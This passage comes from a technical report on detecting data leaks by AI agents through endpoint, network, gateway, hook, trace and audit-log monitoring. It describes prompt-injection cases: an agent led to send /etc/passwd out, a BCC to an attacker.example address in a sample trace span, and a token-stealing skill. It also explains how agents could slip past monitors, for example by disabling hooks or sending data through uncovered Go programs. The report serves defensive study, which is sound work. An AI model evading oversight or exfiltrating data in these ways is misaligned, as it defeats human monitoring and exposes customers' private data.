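Bao and colleagues' tool, AgentLoupe, shows that one observer can collect both kinds of evidence, even without a sandbox. It runs in the Linux kernel, reads messages to the model just before they are encrypted, and labels the files and connections that result from each one. In the staged attack, it traced the later connection back to the original request. The evidence is only two case studies, and the researchers have not measured how often the labels are wrong. Still, the third premise is false for an agent whose requests and effects all pass through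 one machine that the company controls.

Most of the agents in this report do not work that way. A sandbox's monitor can record an email as it leaves, but not what an outside mail service then does with it. If the fake Postmark package ran inside the sandbox, the monitor could find the added address in the outgoing request, but if an outsider hosted the same server, the address would be added outside the sandbox, where the monitor could not detect it. When a vendor runs the whole agent in its cloud, the company has no machine to install a monitor on.

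A sandbox can be enough if the agent never needs to send anything out. Saltzer and Schroeder use the term confinement for letting a borrowed program use data but not release it. A company could run the model locally and block every outgoing connection, and nobody would have to interpret the agent's actions to prevent a disclosure. But an agent that emails customers has to release some data to do its job.

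The argument therefore holds for agents that use outside services, but not for every agent. For agents that do use them, a second vantage point helps only if the team can match its records to those from the first. Matching by time may work when a prompt arrives at 10:13 and a file opens at 10:14. It becomes guesswork when the agent is running twenty tasks, and it fails when the effect comes days after the request.

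## Observing from the machine and the network

Requests are easiest to match to their effects when one computer handles both, as when an agent runs on an employee's laptop. Software on that laptop can link a connection to the process that opened it. A device on the company's network cannot identify processes, but it can monitor computers that have no monitoring software installed. Both may miss an agent that runs in a vendor's cloud.

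### How the machine records an event

Whenever a program opens a file, starts another program or connects to another computer, it makes a system call to the kernel, the core of the operating system. EDR software records these calls. On Linux, many products do so with eBPF, which lets them run small programs inside the kernel. Suppose an agent starts a shell, the program that carries out typed commands:

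1. Before the agent runs, the EDR software loads an eBPF program and attaches it to the point in the kernel where new processes start. The kernel first verifies that the eBPF program will finish and will not touch memory it has no right to use.
2. The agent asks the kernel to start the shell, and the kernel runs the eBPF program while handling the request.
3. The eBPF program notes the command, the user, the time and the process that made the request, and puts these details in a buffer.
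4. The main part of the EDR software reads the buffer, discards what it does not need and sends the rest to the security team's server.

File and network events work the same way. Microsoft describes attachment points for system calls, network connections, and file reads and writes. On Windows, the kernel notifies drivers of similar events, and the drivers pass them to EDR products. Because each new process has a parent, the software can link an agent to the shell it started, the script the shell ran, and the connection the script opened.

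However, EDR products often don't record file opens. Trend Micro, a security vendor, says its Linux software records process starts, new files and outgoing connections under standard settings, but file opens only in a "hypersensitive mode". Its Windows software also requires this mode for file opens. Sysmon for Linux, a free logging tool from Microsoft, recorded file creation and deletion when it came out, but LinuxSecurity's *Lead Microsoft Engineer Kevin Sheldrake Brings Sysmon to Linux* does not list file opens among the tool's events. One likely reason for leaving them out is the volume of data. A sample output that Microsoft publishes shows about 1.7 million system calls of a single type in 20 seconds, most likely from a program designed to stress the machine.

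Reads are therefore the events EDR is most likely to miss. In the John Doe example, standard settings would record the new file in step 2, but usually only its name and location. The read in step 1 goes to a remote database, so it appears on the laptop as a connection. Even hypersensitive mode would not show which record the agent opened.

Coverage also varies between machines. Microsoft's Linux sensor uses eBPF by default but falls back to Netlink, an older source of events, on kernels that do not support eBPF. Netlink reports process starts but not connections or file events such as renames and deletions.

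### Finding the agent among other programs

These events are useful only if the team knows which processes belong to an agent. For well-known products, a catalog of names and file locations can be enough to identify them. Microsoft claims that Defender for Endpoint, its EDR product, discovers more than 20 kinds of local agent. But it counts each combination of user, device and agent type as one agent. If an employee uses Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, for 15 tasks in separate project folders on one device, the inventory lists it once. The team cannot tell from that entry which task opened a connection.

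An agent can also be a script of a few dozen lines with no product name. *Detecting Shadow AI* (Canale and Soulis, 2026) compares the traces that two agents left on one Windows computer. Claude Code left a recognizable program, settings folders, a code editor extension and a history of past projects. A homemade agent left only a shell and a connection to a model provider.

Developers' ordinary tools routinely start a shell while they have an encrypted connection open, for example when they download and install software packages, so a rule that flags any script doing this would flag them too. To test such rules, Canale and Soulis wrote "behavioural twins" of their agents, which were the same programs except that they contacted an ordinary web service instead of a model. Two rules based only on processes and connections flagged every twin as an agent.

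Canale and Soulis's tool, Agent Detector, also checks whether the remote service is a known model provider. It flagged no twins and found every agent in most of five runs. Its main weakness is that many providers share internet addresses with unrelated services, so the tool can identify them only while Windows still stores the name it looked up, which it did for one to five minutes in the tests. It found an intermittently running agent in about a third of scans and missed agents inside WSL 2, a Linux environment that runs within Windows. The test used 12 artificial agents on one workstation, which Canale and Soulis consider too few to rank detectors. The tool finds agents but does not record what data they read.

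### Reading model traffic before encryption

Agents normally encrypt their traffic to a remote model with TLS, the standard encryption for web connections. The agent's process encrypts the data before handing it to the kernel, so an eBPF program that observes only the kernel gets unreadable text. Pixie, an open-source monitoring project, explains how to capture the readable text. Programs usually leave encryption to a library such as OpenSSL, whose SSL_write function encrypts outgoing text and whose SSL_read function decrypts incoming text. A user-space probe, or uprobe, makes the kernel run an eBPF program whenever another program reaches a chosen instruction. A uprobe on SSL_write can copy the text just before encryption, and one on SSL_read can copy it just after decryption.

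The agent's developer does not have to change anything. The monitor needs no encryption keys, but it does need full control of the machine, because only the administrator account can run tools like the one described in Debian's *sslsniff(8)*.

The probe also has to find the right function. This is simple when a program uses the operating system's shared copy of OpenSSL, but some programs contain their own SSL library. In February 2026, Claude Code contained one called BoringSSL, stripped of the labels that show where each function begins. *Reverse Engineering Claude Code's SSL Traffic with eBPF* (eunomia, 2026) describes how standard tools failed and how eunomia's engineers found the functions by comparing byte patterns with a labeled build of the same open-source software.

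Programs written in Go or Rust may never call these functions, because those languages have their own encryption libraries. The maker of a monitoring tool called Heron acknowledges on Product Hunt, a site where developers present new products, that its probes do not automatically cover such programs. An agent could therefore write and run a small Go program that sends data out without the probe reading it, even if the probe reads all of the agent's conversations with the model.

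### AgentSight

*AgentSight* (2025) describes a research tool of the same name that combines these probes with kernel events. Its intent stream contains the prompts and responses that the probes copy from the encryption library. Its action stream contains process starts, file opens, connections and other system calls. A filter in the kernel keeps the action stream manageable by following every process the agent starts and dropping events from the rest of the machine.

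AgentSight then uses three clues to link a model response to the actions it caused:

- **Process tree:** the agent, or a process descended from it, performed the action.
- **Time:** the action came shortly after the response, within a window of 100 to 500 milliseconds.
- **Matching arguments:** a filename, web address or command in the response appears again in a system call.

Finally, a second language model reads the combined record, explains whether anything looks suspicious and gives a confidence score.

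The paper claims that the clues together definitively establish cause and effect, which is too strong. If the model tells the agent to run a script, the response may not name the files the script opens, and a long-running script will open many of them after the time window has closed. The process tree still connects those files to the agent, but not to a particular response. If the computer's scheduler starts the script an hour later, the process tree no longer connects the files to the agent either, a problem that Bao and colleagues' AgentLoupe addresses.

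The AgentSight paper measures how much the tool slows down Claude Code on three tasks, each run three times with the tool and three times without it. Examining a code repository took 132.33 seconds instead of 127.98 (3.4% longer), writing code took 23.64 instead of 22.54 (4.9%), and compiling a repository took 92.72 instead of 92.40 (0.4%). The abstract's figure of "less than 3%" is the average of the three, and two of the tasks exceeded it. The slowdown is small, but the exact percentages are unreliable because a model's response time can easily vary by a second or more between runs, and the paper does not report how much the three runs differed.

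The security evidence is one staged attack. The researchers asked an agent to download and build a software project whose instructions directed the agent to a web page with a hidden prompt. The prompt instructed it to read /etc/passwd, a file that lists a Linux computer's user accounts, and send it to an outside server as if this were part of the build. AgentSight recorded 521 events and merged them into 37, from the visit to the web page to the final transmission. The second model flagged the agent's actions as inconsistent with its task and rated an attack as highly likely.

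AgentSight did not stop the theft, because the record that the second model judged already contained the transmission. The paper reports only one attack and no count of false alarms during ordinary work, so readers cannot tell from it how often the tool would miss an attack or raise a false alarm. The other two cases concern performance. In one, an agent kept repeating a failed web search, and in the other, six coding agents delayed each other by locking files.

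A tool like this also creates new copies of the data it monitors. In the running example, the intent stream would contain John Doe's record. AgentSight's documentation advises users to treat its logs and databases as sensitive. If an outside provider runs the second model, analyzing the record means submitting it again.

### Endpoint DLP

Endpoint DLP runs on the employee's computer and can block a transfer as well as record it. It typically checks a file when someone copies it to a USB drive, prints it or uploads it through a browser. It reads the file on the machine, so it works even when network traffic is encrypted.

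Agents can easily bypass these checkpoints without intending to. In the example, the record goes from the database into the agent's memory and then into an email, and no one uploads a file. A script can also read a file and send its contents over its own connection. Some products can stop listed programs from opening sensitive files, but a homemade agent may run as python.exe, which also runs many harmless scripts. Blocking python.exe would stop those scripts too.

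A company can also block destinations. Microsoft's *Overview of network protection* describes a feature that blocks web requests to disreputable domains from any program, not just a browser. The feature could have stopped the theft in AgentSight's test if the outside server had been on its list of blocked domains. It would not stop the BCC in the John Doe example, because the agent sends that email through a mail service the company has approved.

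### Proxies and TLS inspection

Companies usually monitor network traffic at a forward proxy, a server that passes on web requests from their machines. To open an encrypted connection, a program sends the proxy a host name, and the proxy connects to that host and relays data it cannot read. The proxy's log can show the time, the machine, the host name and the amount of data.

Security products compare such logs with a catalog of known services. Canale and Soulis report that Microsoft's catalog lists more than 31,000 applications, including categories for model providers and MCP servers, but that applications missing from it cannot be discovered. Even a correct match gives little information. If an approved assistant and an employee's unapproved script use the same model provider, the log shows the same host for both. If an agent reaches its model through OpenRouter, the log shows OpenRouter,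 not the company running the model. A model running on the laptop itself produces no entry.

To read the content, the proxy has to perform TLS inspection. TLS normally prevents this because the program checks a certificate, a signed statement that a certain encryption key belongs to a certain site. The company gets around the check as follows:

1. The IT department adds the company's own certificate authority to the list of signers that each managed machine trusts.
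2. When the agent connects to the mail service, the proxy answers in its place, with a certificate it has just created in the mail service's name.
3. The agent's software accepts the certificate because the machine trusts the signer.
4. The proxy decrypts the request, scans it, and sends it to the real mail service over a second encrypted connection.

Step 3 fails if the program uses certificate pinning, meaning it accepts only a certificate or signer its developers chose in advance. The connection then breaks, and the IT department has to exempt the service from inspection or do without the program. Some programming tools also use their own list of trusted signers instead of the machine's until someone changes a setting. Exempting a service leaves a permanent gap in monitoring, which is tempting to exploit if the service is a model provider, because agents send so much company data there.

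TLS inspection also fails on unmanaged devices, such as a contractor's laptop, because they do not trust the company's certificate authority. Managed laptops need software that sends their traffic through the proxy even when employees work from home. Many inspection products cannot handle HTTP/3, a newer version of the web's protocol, because it uses a different kind of connection.

### AI gateways and browser extensions

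An AI gateway is a server between agents and model providers that can scan and record every prompt and response. It avoids the certificate problem because the agent connects to it directly. The company replaces the provider's address with the gateway's, often by changing one setting, and the gateway forwards each request to the provider. Examples are Cloudflare AI Gateway and LiteLLM, which a company can run on its own servers.

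For the four tool calls in the example, the gateway would handle at least five requests to the model, one to get each call and one to get the final answer. Each request contains the context so far, so John Doe's record would pass through about four times. A DLP rule that counts every match as a new event would therefore report a single read of the record as several. The gateway also receives each tool call before the agent's software does, so it can in principle block the call.

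However, an agent that can change its own settings may be able to bypass the gateway. The company can prevent this by keeping the provider's keys only on the gateway and blocking direct connections to model providers. Some gaps remain because an employee may have a personal key, and a relay can offer a well-known model under a domain name that no blocklist contains.

A browser extension can monitor how employees use AI services through web pages. It can read a page after the browser has decrypted it, so it can check what an employee types or pastes and warn them before they send it. It works on any network, but only in browsers where it is installed, and it does not cover agents in a terminal or desktop application. If an agent operates the browser, the extension may record the agent's clicks as the employee's.

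### What encrypted traffic reveals

A network monitor that cannot decrypt traffic can still record the size, direction and timing of each packet, the small unit in which data crosses a network. These measurements can reveal a lot about what an agent is doing. In *Exposing LLM User Privacy via Traffic Fingerprint Analysis*, Zhang, Deng and colleagues (2025) recorded encrypted traffic between users and vendor-hosted agents. A web search produced one burst of data for the retrieval and another for the summary, while image generation began with a short text, then a pause, then a large burst.

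Zhang and colleagues trained a classifier on labeled recordings and tested it on new ones. It recognized which of five kinds of activity an agent was performing with 94.1% accuracy, and identified which of 50 agents was in use with an F1 score of 0.866. When the test included agents the classifier had never encountered, the median score stayed above 0.80. However, the researchers wrote their prompts to trigger each agent's main function, and they acknowledge that a generic question leaves a much weaker fingerprint, so real use would probably be harder to classify.

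Pouryousef, Lopez and colleagues (2026), in *A Large-Scale Benchmark and Risk Assessment of Traffic Analysis Attacks*, also studied groups of agents. Their classifier distinguished ten tasks, such as coding, contract analysis and bargaining, with up to 90.7% accuracy, compared with about 10% for guessing. It could still detect the tasks from only one agent's traffic. In ordinary conversations with a model, the classifier had 97.7% accuracy in identifying which of ten models was responding and 76.7% in identifying which of six kinds of prompt the user had sent.

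These results come from favorable conditions. Pouryousef and colleagues ran the models on their own server, used the same small model for every agent in a group, and assumed that the observer knows where each interaction starts and ends. Every recording also belonged to one of the categories in the training data. The paper gives the number of group runs as 2,838 in one place and 3,970 in another.

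The larger problem for a security team is that none of the categories is a leak. A classifier may recognize that an agent is writing an email, but not that the email has the wrong recipient. At 94.1% accuracy, it would also mislabel about 590 of every 10,000 sessions. Fingerprinting is more useful for finding agents that nobody declared, but even then it can reveal personal information about employees. Zhang and colleagues used people's patterns of agent use over time to guess their occupations from 12 categories. Three guesses included the correct category 73.9% of the time for simulated users and 69.1% of the time for 49 real participants.

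### The extra address from both vantage points

Whether a monitor can detect the extra address in the John Doe email depends partly on how the address got there. Prompt injection could have put it in the tool call, or the fake Postmark package could have added it afterwards. The table assumes that the agent and the package both run on an employee's managed laptop.

| Monitor | Address in the tool call | Address added by the package |
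|---|---|---|
| EDR, standard settings | Not visible | Not visible |
| Probe on the agent's encryption library | Visible | Visible only if the probe also covers the package's process |
| Proxy without decryption | Not visible | Not visible |
| Proxy with TLS inspection of model and mail traffic | Visible | Visible |
| AI gateway | Visible | Not visible |

EDR would record that the agent started the package and that the package connected to a mail service, both of which are normal. A proxy without decryption would not reveal the copying through traffic volume either, because the mail service makes the second copy of the email itself, and the company's outgoing traffic grows only by the length of one address.

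A monitor that can read the address still needs a way to detect that it is wrong, because without the employee's request, the mail traffic shows only an ordinary email with a BCC. To catch the fake package, the team would have to compare the tool call with the request that left the laptop and notice the extra recipient in the outgoing request. A probe or a TLS-inspecting proxy can supply both texts, but someone has to build the comparison.

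### Competing claims of blindness

A proxy with TLS inspection or an AI gateway can read what an agent sends over an encrypted connection, but a device that only records packets cannot. Vendors often describe each other's vantage points as blind, and wolfSSL, which sells an encryption library, makes this argument about packet capture in *From TLS Blindness to Full Visibility*. The company argues that eBPF probes get the readable text and identify the process that sent it.

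For programs that Heron's probes do not cover, its maker recommends capturing the traffic at a gateway or another point where it is already readable. This concession is more informative because it goes against the maker's interest. It means the probes must be supplemented with network capture in the cases where they are most likely to miss a homemade tool.

The argument against relying on endpoint software is that it protects only the machines it is installed on and only the programs it recognizes. Microsoft's documentation largely supports this. Its newer protection for local agents takes prompts and tool calls directly from the agent's software, and Microsoft initially listed only two supported agents. Directions on Microsoft (2026) describes the range as "narrow but important". Without this connection, Microsoft Defender can still record what happens on the machine, but later and with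 less context, as pisinger points out in *Stopping Prompt Injection at the Endpoint*.

For some agents that offer no such connection, Defender inspects the traffic between agent and model on the laptop. Appel's *Configure AI agent runtime protection preview with Microsoft Defender for Endpoint* lists four supported applications, including ChatGPT Desktop in chat mode. The feature does not work with certificate pinning or HTTP/3, which also cause network proxies to fail. It looks for prompt injection, not for customer data in the wrong place.

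Which programs' traffic a monitor can read therefore matters more than whether its vendor sells endpoint or network products. Canale and Soulis come closest to an overall comparison. They judge that proxies only partly detect homemade agents and miss local models entirely, while software inventories on the machine find known products but miss homemade agents. However, they built an endpoint tool themselves, and they describe the comparison as a summary of designs, not measurements. None of these sources ran both kinds of monitor on the same agents and counted what each missed.

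### An agent in a vendor's cloud

If the company builds the same agent in Copilot Studio instead, the employee types the request into a web page and Microsoft's servers run the loop. If the customer database, mail service and support system are also cloud services, all four tool calls travel between data centers that the company does not own. Canale and Soulis exclude such agents from their study because they have no footprint on the laptop.

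The laptop's EDR would record a browser connecting to Microsoft. TLS inspection or a browser extension could also capture the employee's request and the agent's reply, perhaps a message that the email to John Doe has gone out. Neither would show the BCC unless the page displayed it. Fingerprinting could at best suggest what kind of work the agent was doing. The ShadowLeak attack exploited this lack of visibility by sending data out from the vendor's servers.

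Part of the agent's work may still pass through the company's network. If the database runs on the company's own servers, a firewall can log the incoming connection from the vendor, and if the agent sends its email through the company's mail gateway, the gateway can check the recipients. But many companies rent both the database and the mail service. If the agent also runs on a schedule, with no employee at a browser, the company's machines and network may record nothing.

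## Observing from inside the agent's software

Every agent needs a program to run its loop. The employee's request, retrieved content, tool inputs, results and messages to other agents all pass through that program as readable text. A team can record them there without decrypting traffic or working out an agent's intent from system calls. But if a vendor runs the program, the company gets only the records the vendor provides.

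Companies can make these records with hooks in the agent program, gateways in front of MCP servers, or traces in the OpenTelemetry format. The methods differ in what they cover and whether they keep the content of tool calls by default.

### Hooks

A hook is a command or web request that an agent program runs at a set point in its loop. Claude Code has more than 30 such points. The most useful ones for monitoring data come when the user submits a prompt and just before and after a tool call.

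According to Anthropic's documentation, a hook that runs before a tool call receives the tool's name, its complete input and an ID for the call. Sample data from Anthropic shows that the hook also receives the session's ID and the location of a file containing the conversation. A hook that runs after the call also receives the tool's response. In the John Doe example, a hook on the email tool would receive both addresses before the email went out, and could read the employee's request in the conversation file.

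Claude Code has no hooks until someone defines them, so by default this method records nothing. Once defined, a hook receives the full content, and the company decides how much to keep. Copilot Studio offers a similar checkpoint for agents that Microsoft hosts.

Hooks also cover work that never appears in the main agent's context. When an agent delegates part of a task, the same hooks run inside the second agent and receive its ID. The delegated instructions are in the input of the tool call that starts the second agent. In some sessions, the second agent delivers its report through a separate tool, so a hook that reads only the result of the original call gets a short note instead of the report.

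Some content reaches the model without any tool call. If an employee mentions a file with the @ sign, Claude Code normally inserts its text into the prompt, so a hook on the file-reading tool never runs. A hook can also miss calls because its filter is too narrow. For example, a hook that matches only the Bash tool will not record commands run through PowerShell, which Claude Code may use on Windows. If the path to a hook's script contains a typo, the script never runs, and by default Claude Code usually shows an error notice and carries out the call anyway.

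### Gateways in front of MCP servers

An MCP gateway is a server that receives requests from agents and forwards them to MCP servers. It sits between an agent and its tools, whereas an AI gateway sits between an agent and its model. An MCP request to run a tool contains the tool's name and inputs, and the reply contains the result, so a gateway can record all three. OpenTelemetry's *MCP* lists standard fields for MCP records, including the type of request, the protocol version and the address of a resource, such as a file or the layout of a customer database.

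One gateway can cover agents from many developers, including agents that have no hooks. But MCP does not specify what a gateway should log. Products differ in whether they keep inputs and results by default, so a team has to check before relying on the log.

Like an MCP server, the gateway would receive the BCC address but not the employee's request. It would also miss an address that the fake Postmark package added. It doesn't receive calls to tools built into the agent program, such as Claude Code's tools for reading files and running commands.

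In principle, the MCP server could supply the missing part. pkg.go.dev's *mcp* (2026), the documentation of a software library, describes how a client can put tracing information in the metadata of each MCP request, so that client and server records join into one trace. This works for servers that report accurately, but the person who wrote the fake Postmark package is unlikely to have reported the extra address.

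Agents can also bypass a gateway. Levine, Lejeail and Mooney report in *What we learned about AI agent security by monitoring our agents* that their employer, the monitoring company Datadog, found internal applications that contacted model providers directly instead of through an AI gateway. An MCP gateway has the same weakness if agents can reach the servers behind it directly. Gateways are also attractive targets because so much data passes through them. In March 2026, attackers published two malicious versions of the AI gateway software LiteLLM on PyPI, a public library of Python packages.

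### OpenTelemetry traces

OpenTelemetry is an open-source project that defines common formats for recording what software does. A span records one operation, such as a call to a model, and a trace joins the spans from the same task. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* defines fields for AI systems so that different monitoring products can read the same records.

A span for a model call records the operation, the provider, the model, and the length of the input and output. It should also include a conversation ID if one is available. The provider's name helps a team notice that the agent sent data to the model's vendor, though the name may be wrong if the request goes through a relay.

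A span for a tool call includes the tool's name and usually its type, its description and the call's ID. The call's inputs and results are optional fields, as are the standing instructions and the messages to and from the model. The version that OpenTelemetry published before moving these conventions to a separate repository in 2026 omits the optional fields unless developers opt in to recording them.

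OpenTelemetry's reasons are storage costs, regulation, and the need to give fewer people access to sensitive content than to operational data. Storage costs are growing. Levine and colleagues report that the average request length for Datadog's median customer more than doubled in a year. For production systems with large or sensitive content, OpenTelemetry recommends storing the content elsewhere, under separate access rules, and putting only a reference to it in the span.

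Recording retrieved documents is also optional, and the minimum record for each is an ID and a relevance score. A team that opts in may therefore know which document the agent retrieved but not have the text it read. This matters if the document contained hidden instructions and someone has since changed it.

### The extra address in a trace

The table shows an invented span for step 3 of the John Doe example. The span uses OpenTelemetry's field names and follows the pattern of a weather tool in OpenTelemetry's *LLM call examples*.

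| Field | Recorded by default | Value |
|---|---|---|
| Trace ID | Yes | Same as for the other steps |
| Span name | Yes | execute_tool send_email |
| gen_ai.operation.name | Yes | execute_tool |
| gen_ai.tool.name | Yes | send_email |
| gen_ai.tool.call.id | Yes, if available | call_3 |
| gen_ai.tool.type | Yes, if available | function |
| gen_ai.tool.call.arguments | No | to: john.doe@example.com; bcc: copies@attacker.example; body: details of John Doe's account |
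| gen_ai.tool.call.result | No | Accepted for delivery |

By default, this span would differ from one for a harmless email only in its IDs and time. The second recipient appears only in the optional inputs.

The span with its inputs directly records only one of the four events, the submission of the email addressed to John Doe and the attacker. It shows that the mail service accepted the email, not that anyone received it. The same call also moves account details into the mail service, which probably keeps a copy in its sent messages. The span doesn't record that movement or copy, but a team that knows how the service works can infer them. The original read, the copy in a file and the movement into a ticket happened in the other tool calls, which have their own spans in the same trace.

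With full content capture, the address can appear both in the model's response, where the model proposes the call, and in the tool's span. Comparing the two can show whether software changed the call in between, as a Claude Code hook can do by rewriting a tool's inputs before the tool runs. If the address appears only in the tool's span, the model did not add it. If the fake Postmark package added it, the address would appear in neither place.

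### What a recorded call leaves out

When an agent runs a script, the agent's software records a command such as "python cleanup.py" and whatever the script prints, but not which files the script opened or sent. If the agent wrote the script, an earlier tool call may contain the code, but the code alone may not show which files the script found when it ran.

Claude Code can list the files that a command changed in a Git repository, a store for source code and its history. Anthropic warns that the list can miss changes or include another program's changes, and advises against using it to enforce a policy. The list also omits files that the command only read and data that it sent, so it would not help with a disclosure.

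A script can produce its own OpenTelemetry spans only if its developer built this in and the script is configured with a destination for them. Claude Code removes OpenTelemetry export settings from every program it starts, so scripts do not inherit the destination. Without separate instrumentation, their activity is missing from the trace.

Commands can even run before the model receives anything. Levine and colleagues describe a malicious skill (an add-on for Claude Code) that Datadog's researchers found in circulation and reproduced in a controlled test. While Claude Code was preparing the skill's text for the model, commands in the skill fetched a GitHub login token and sent it to a destination the attacker controlled. The model later refused to run the skill, but the token had already been sent. Someone who read only the model's inputs and outputs might have concluded that the refusal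 had stopped the attack.

An agent may also be able to change the software that records it. Claude Code reads hooks from settings files, including one in the project folder, and normally picks up edits automatically. A single setting turns off the hooks defined by users and projects, so an agent with permission to edit these files could stop the recording, perhaps because it was following a hidden instruction. An administrator can prevent this by defining hooks in centrally managed settings, since user and project settings cannot disable those hooks. A hook can also immediately send each record to a remote server, where later changes on the laptop will not affect it. These measures offer less protection if the agent has administrator rights, since it could then replace the agent program itself.

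### Linking an action to the text behind it

Despite these gaps, the agent's software can link a tool call to the text the model received and to the tool's result more directly than monitoring on the machine or the network can. The same program handles all three and can label them with shared IDs. AgentSight has to infer these links. An AI gateway can read the same text, but its only evidence that a tool ran is the agent's next request to the model.

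Levine and colleagues found that ordinary application logs could contain an agent's final request to another system without the prompt, document or tool result that led to it. Once they could connect the events in a whole session, they built a rule that matched when a session contained both a prompt flagged as an attempt to extract data and a tool result containing credentials or certain personal data. They did not focus on general email addresses, because agents may handle those in routine work. A match gave responders something to investigate but did not prove that data had left the company. They do not report how often the rule was right, and Datadog sells the product they used.

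Recording the text and the action together does not prove what caused the action. The hidden instruction in John Doe's record is strong evidence of an attack, but the team still has to infer why the model added the address.

For tools with structured inputs, such as email, the agent's software is usually the best place to judge what the agent was trying to do. It makes sense to record at least the recipients, even if the company leaves out the rest of the content. For agents that mostly run scripts, a record from the agent's software is much less informative, and a team also needs one from the machine where the scripts run.

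### Official guidance and shared formats

CISA (2026), the US cybersecurity agency, announced joint guidance on AI agents by six agencies from the US, Australia, Canada, New Zealand and the UK on May 1, 2026. The Australian Cyber Security Centre's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026) advises organizations to consider lower-risk alternatives for repetitive work, anticipate what could go wrong, and establish "ongoing visibility and assurance". A default OpenTelemetry trace would provide little of this visibility in the John Doe case because it would omit the recipients.

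NIST, the US standards institute, plans to publish security controls for agents as overlays, which adapt its general catalog of controls to a particular use. *Control Overlays for Securing AI Systems Concept Paper and Slack Channel* includes both single agents and groups of agents among the planned uses. NIST intended to publish the overlays one use at a time, starting in early fiscal year 2026. The discussion draft it released in January 2026, *COSAiS Predictive AI annotated outline*, covers predictive AI, not agents. The project is now called Control Overlays for Super Intelligence Systems, and NIST still describes the series as something it "will develop". Companies therefore appear to have no finished NIST overlay to consult on what to log for agents.

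A shared event format would let a team search for the same activity across agents from different vendors. Currently, even the tool's name has different labels, "tool_name" in Claude Code's hooks and "gen_ai.tool.name" in OpenTelemetry. OpenTelemetry's conventions are also unfinished. Wang (2026), in *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions*, reports that the conventions moved to their own repository in June 2026 and had no official release there as of August 21.

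The database vendor Greptime (2026) lists changes to OpenTelemetry's AI conventions in every version from 1.37 to 1.41, including new fields for MCP in 1.39. Version 1.37 renamed the field for the model provider, so a search for the old name will miss records in the new format. OpenTelemetry tells developers of existing tools not to switch versions by default, so a company may have to search for both names.

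*Security Event Framework for AI Systems* (Iqbal, 2025) proposes a format designed for security teams. Its fields include the sensitivity of the data, the amount transferred, and separate IDs for the user and the agent. Iqbal works for the security vendor Zscaler. The paper is an Internet-Draft, a working document of the body that develops internet standards, and this version was due to expire on June 25, 2026.

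Iqbal's draft lists tool inputs among the details to capture, but its sample record of a tool call omits them. A record like the sample would show that the agent used the email tool on confidential data, but it would not show the extra recipient. The draft's test covered 28 minutes of proxy logs from one company and identified one AI code editor, which accounted for 57 of 525 network sessions. The test shows that real traffic can fill some of the fields, but it provides little evidence about whether the format would work for other agents.

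## Application logs and the vendor's cloud

The customer database, mail service and file store that an agent uses normally keep their own audit logs, wherever the agent runs. If a vendor runs the agent in its cloud, the company may have only these logs and whatever records the vendor shares.

### What an application records about a read

When an agent opens John Doe's record in step 1 of the running example, a detailed log entry would contain the time, the account, the program that presented the token, the object, the number of rows returned and the network address of the request.

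The object and the row count describe what data the application released. An agent looking for John Doe might search for him by name or retrieve the whole customer table. The object may be "customers" either way, so only the row count, 1 or 40,000, distinguishes a lookup from a bulk copy. Some applications log every change to the data but log reads only if an administrator turns on a more detailed setting, and some log the text of a query but not the number of rows it returned.

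A request's source address is of limited use in identifying an agent. An agent on an employee's laptop has the same address as the employee's browser. A request from an agent in a vendor's cloud comes from the vendor's data center. That address suggests that software made the request, but many of the vendor's customers may share it.

Whether the entry identifies the agent depends mostly on how the agent signs in:

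| How the agent signs in | What the log entry shows |
|---|---|
| With an account of its own | The agent, but usually not the employee who gave it the task |
| With an OAuth token that an employee approved | The employee, plus the agent's software if the application logs which program used the token |
| In the employee's logged-in session | Only the employee |
| With a shared service account or key | Only the shared account |

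Even with a token, the entry usually identifies a product, such as ChatGPT, and not a particular agent or conversation.

A company that makes both the application and the agent can log more. According to Microsoft, the audit record for its Copilot assistants includes the user, the agent's ID and name, and a list of the files, emails and other items that Copilot accessed. For each item, the record can show whether Copilot read, created or modified it, whether the attempt succeeded, and which sensitivity label the customer had attached to it. It also shows whether Microsoft detected a prompt injection in the item.

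A security team that searches the log only for FileAccessed entries will miss everything Copilot read. The log records a FileAccessed entry when an employee opens a file in SharePoint, Microsoft's service for shared documents. If Copilot opens the file for the employee, the log records a CopilotInteraction entry instead, as Pistachio's *Copilot Broke Your Audit Log, but Microsoft Won’t Tell You* explains. Pistachio, which sells security training, considers this correct because the employee did not open the file directly.

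### Logs of OAuth grants

The log entry for an OAuth grant, in which an employee or administrator approves a token's scopes, typically contains the person, the program, the scopes and the time. Both the company whose system issues the token and the AI vendor whose agent will use it can log the grant.

According to Elastic, which sells log-search software, OpenAI's logs for business customers record when apps are linked or unlinked. Anthropic's *Query compliance activities* lists events for an employee connecting to an integration, an administrator adding an MCP server, and an attempt to obtain a token for an MCP server through the company's central login. Anthropic may report repeated failures with the same cause only once, so a team can't use these entries to count attempts.

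Grant logs are good for finding agents that nobody declared. If an employee connects an unapproved assistant to a work mailbox from a home computer, EDR and the company's network monitors record nothing, but the mail service can log the grant. The grant's scopes also limit what the agent can read with that token.

However, the grant log doesn't record reads, and one grant can cover months of them. The log also adds no entry when a thief uses a token that an employee approved earlier, as in the Salesloft Drift theft of 2025. An agent that works in an employee's logged-in browser session needs no new grant.

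### What the compliance exports contain

OpenAI, Anthropic and Microsoft each let business customers retrieve records of how their employees use AI. These compliance exports differ most in whether they include the text of prompts, answers and tool calls.

For each message, Microsoft's audit record contains an ID, a marker showing whether it is a prompt or a response, and a marker for detected attempts to get around the model's safety rules, but not the message text. The common fields that Microsoft documents do not include the inputs to tool calls either. If the agent in the example ran in Copilot Studio, the audit record could identify the agent and the items it opened but would not show the BCC address.

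Anthropic's Compliance API exports events through a feed and content through separate requests. The feed covers more than 600 event types and shows who did what and when, but Anthropic's *Compliance API FAQ* states that the feed contains no prompts or responses. Customers on the Claude Enterprise plan can get those by requesting chat text or agent session transcripts. The transcripts include tool calls and their results, so they would show the BCC address if the model wrote it.

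By default, Anthropic cuts each tool input and each piece of text in a result to 10,000 bytes, which is enough for an ordinary email but not for a long list of customers. A team can request a limit of up to about 1 MiB (roughly a million characters of plain English text).

The transcripts leave out images and the model's reasoning. Anthropic's *Design your compliance integration* adds that they omit tool definitions and MCP server configurations. For the fake Postmark package, a transcript might therefore show a call to an email tool but not which package provided it.

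OpenAI's logs also contain text. Elastic lists conversation messages, requests to connected apps and their responses, and the tool calls, prompts and responses of Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. It also lists runs, memory access and calls to connected services for agents that a company builds in its ChatGPT workspace. A December 2025 update to OpenAI's *New compliance and administrative tools for ChatGPT Enterprise* (2024) describes the exports as immutable log files, each covering a set period. Immutability protects entries from later changes but doesn't ensure that OpenAI recorded every event.

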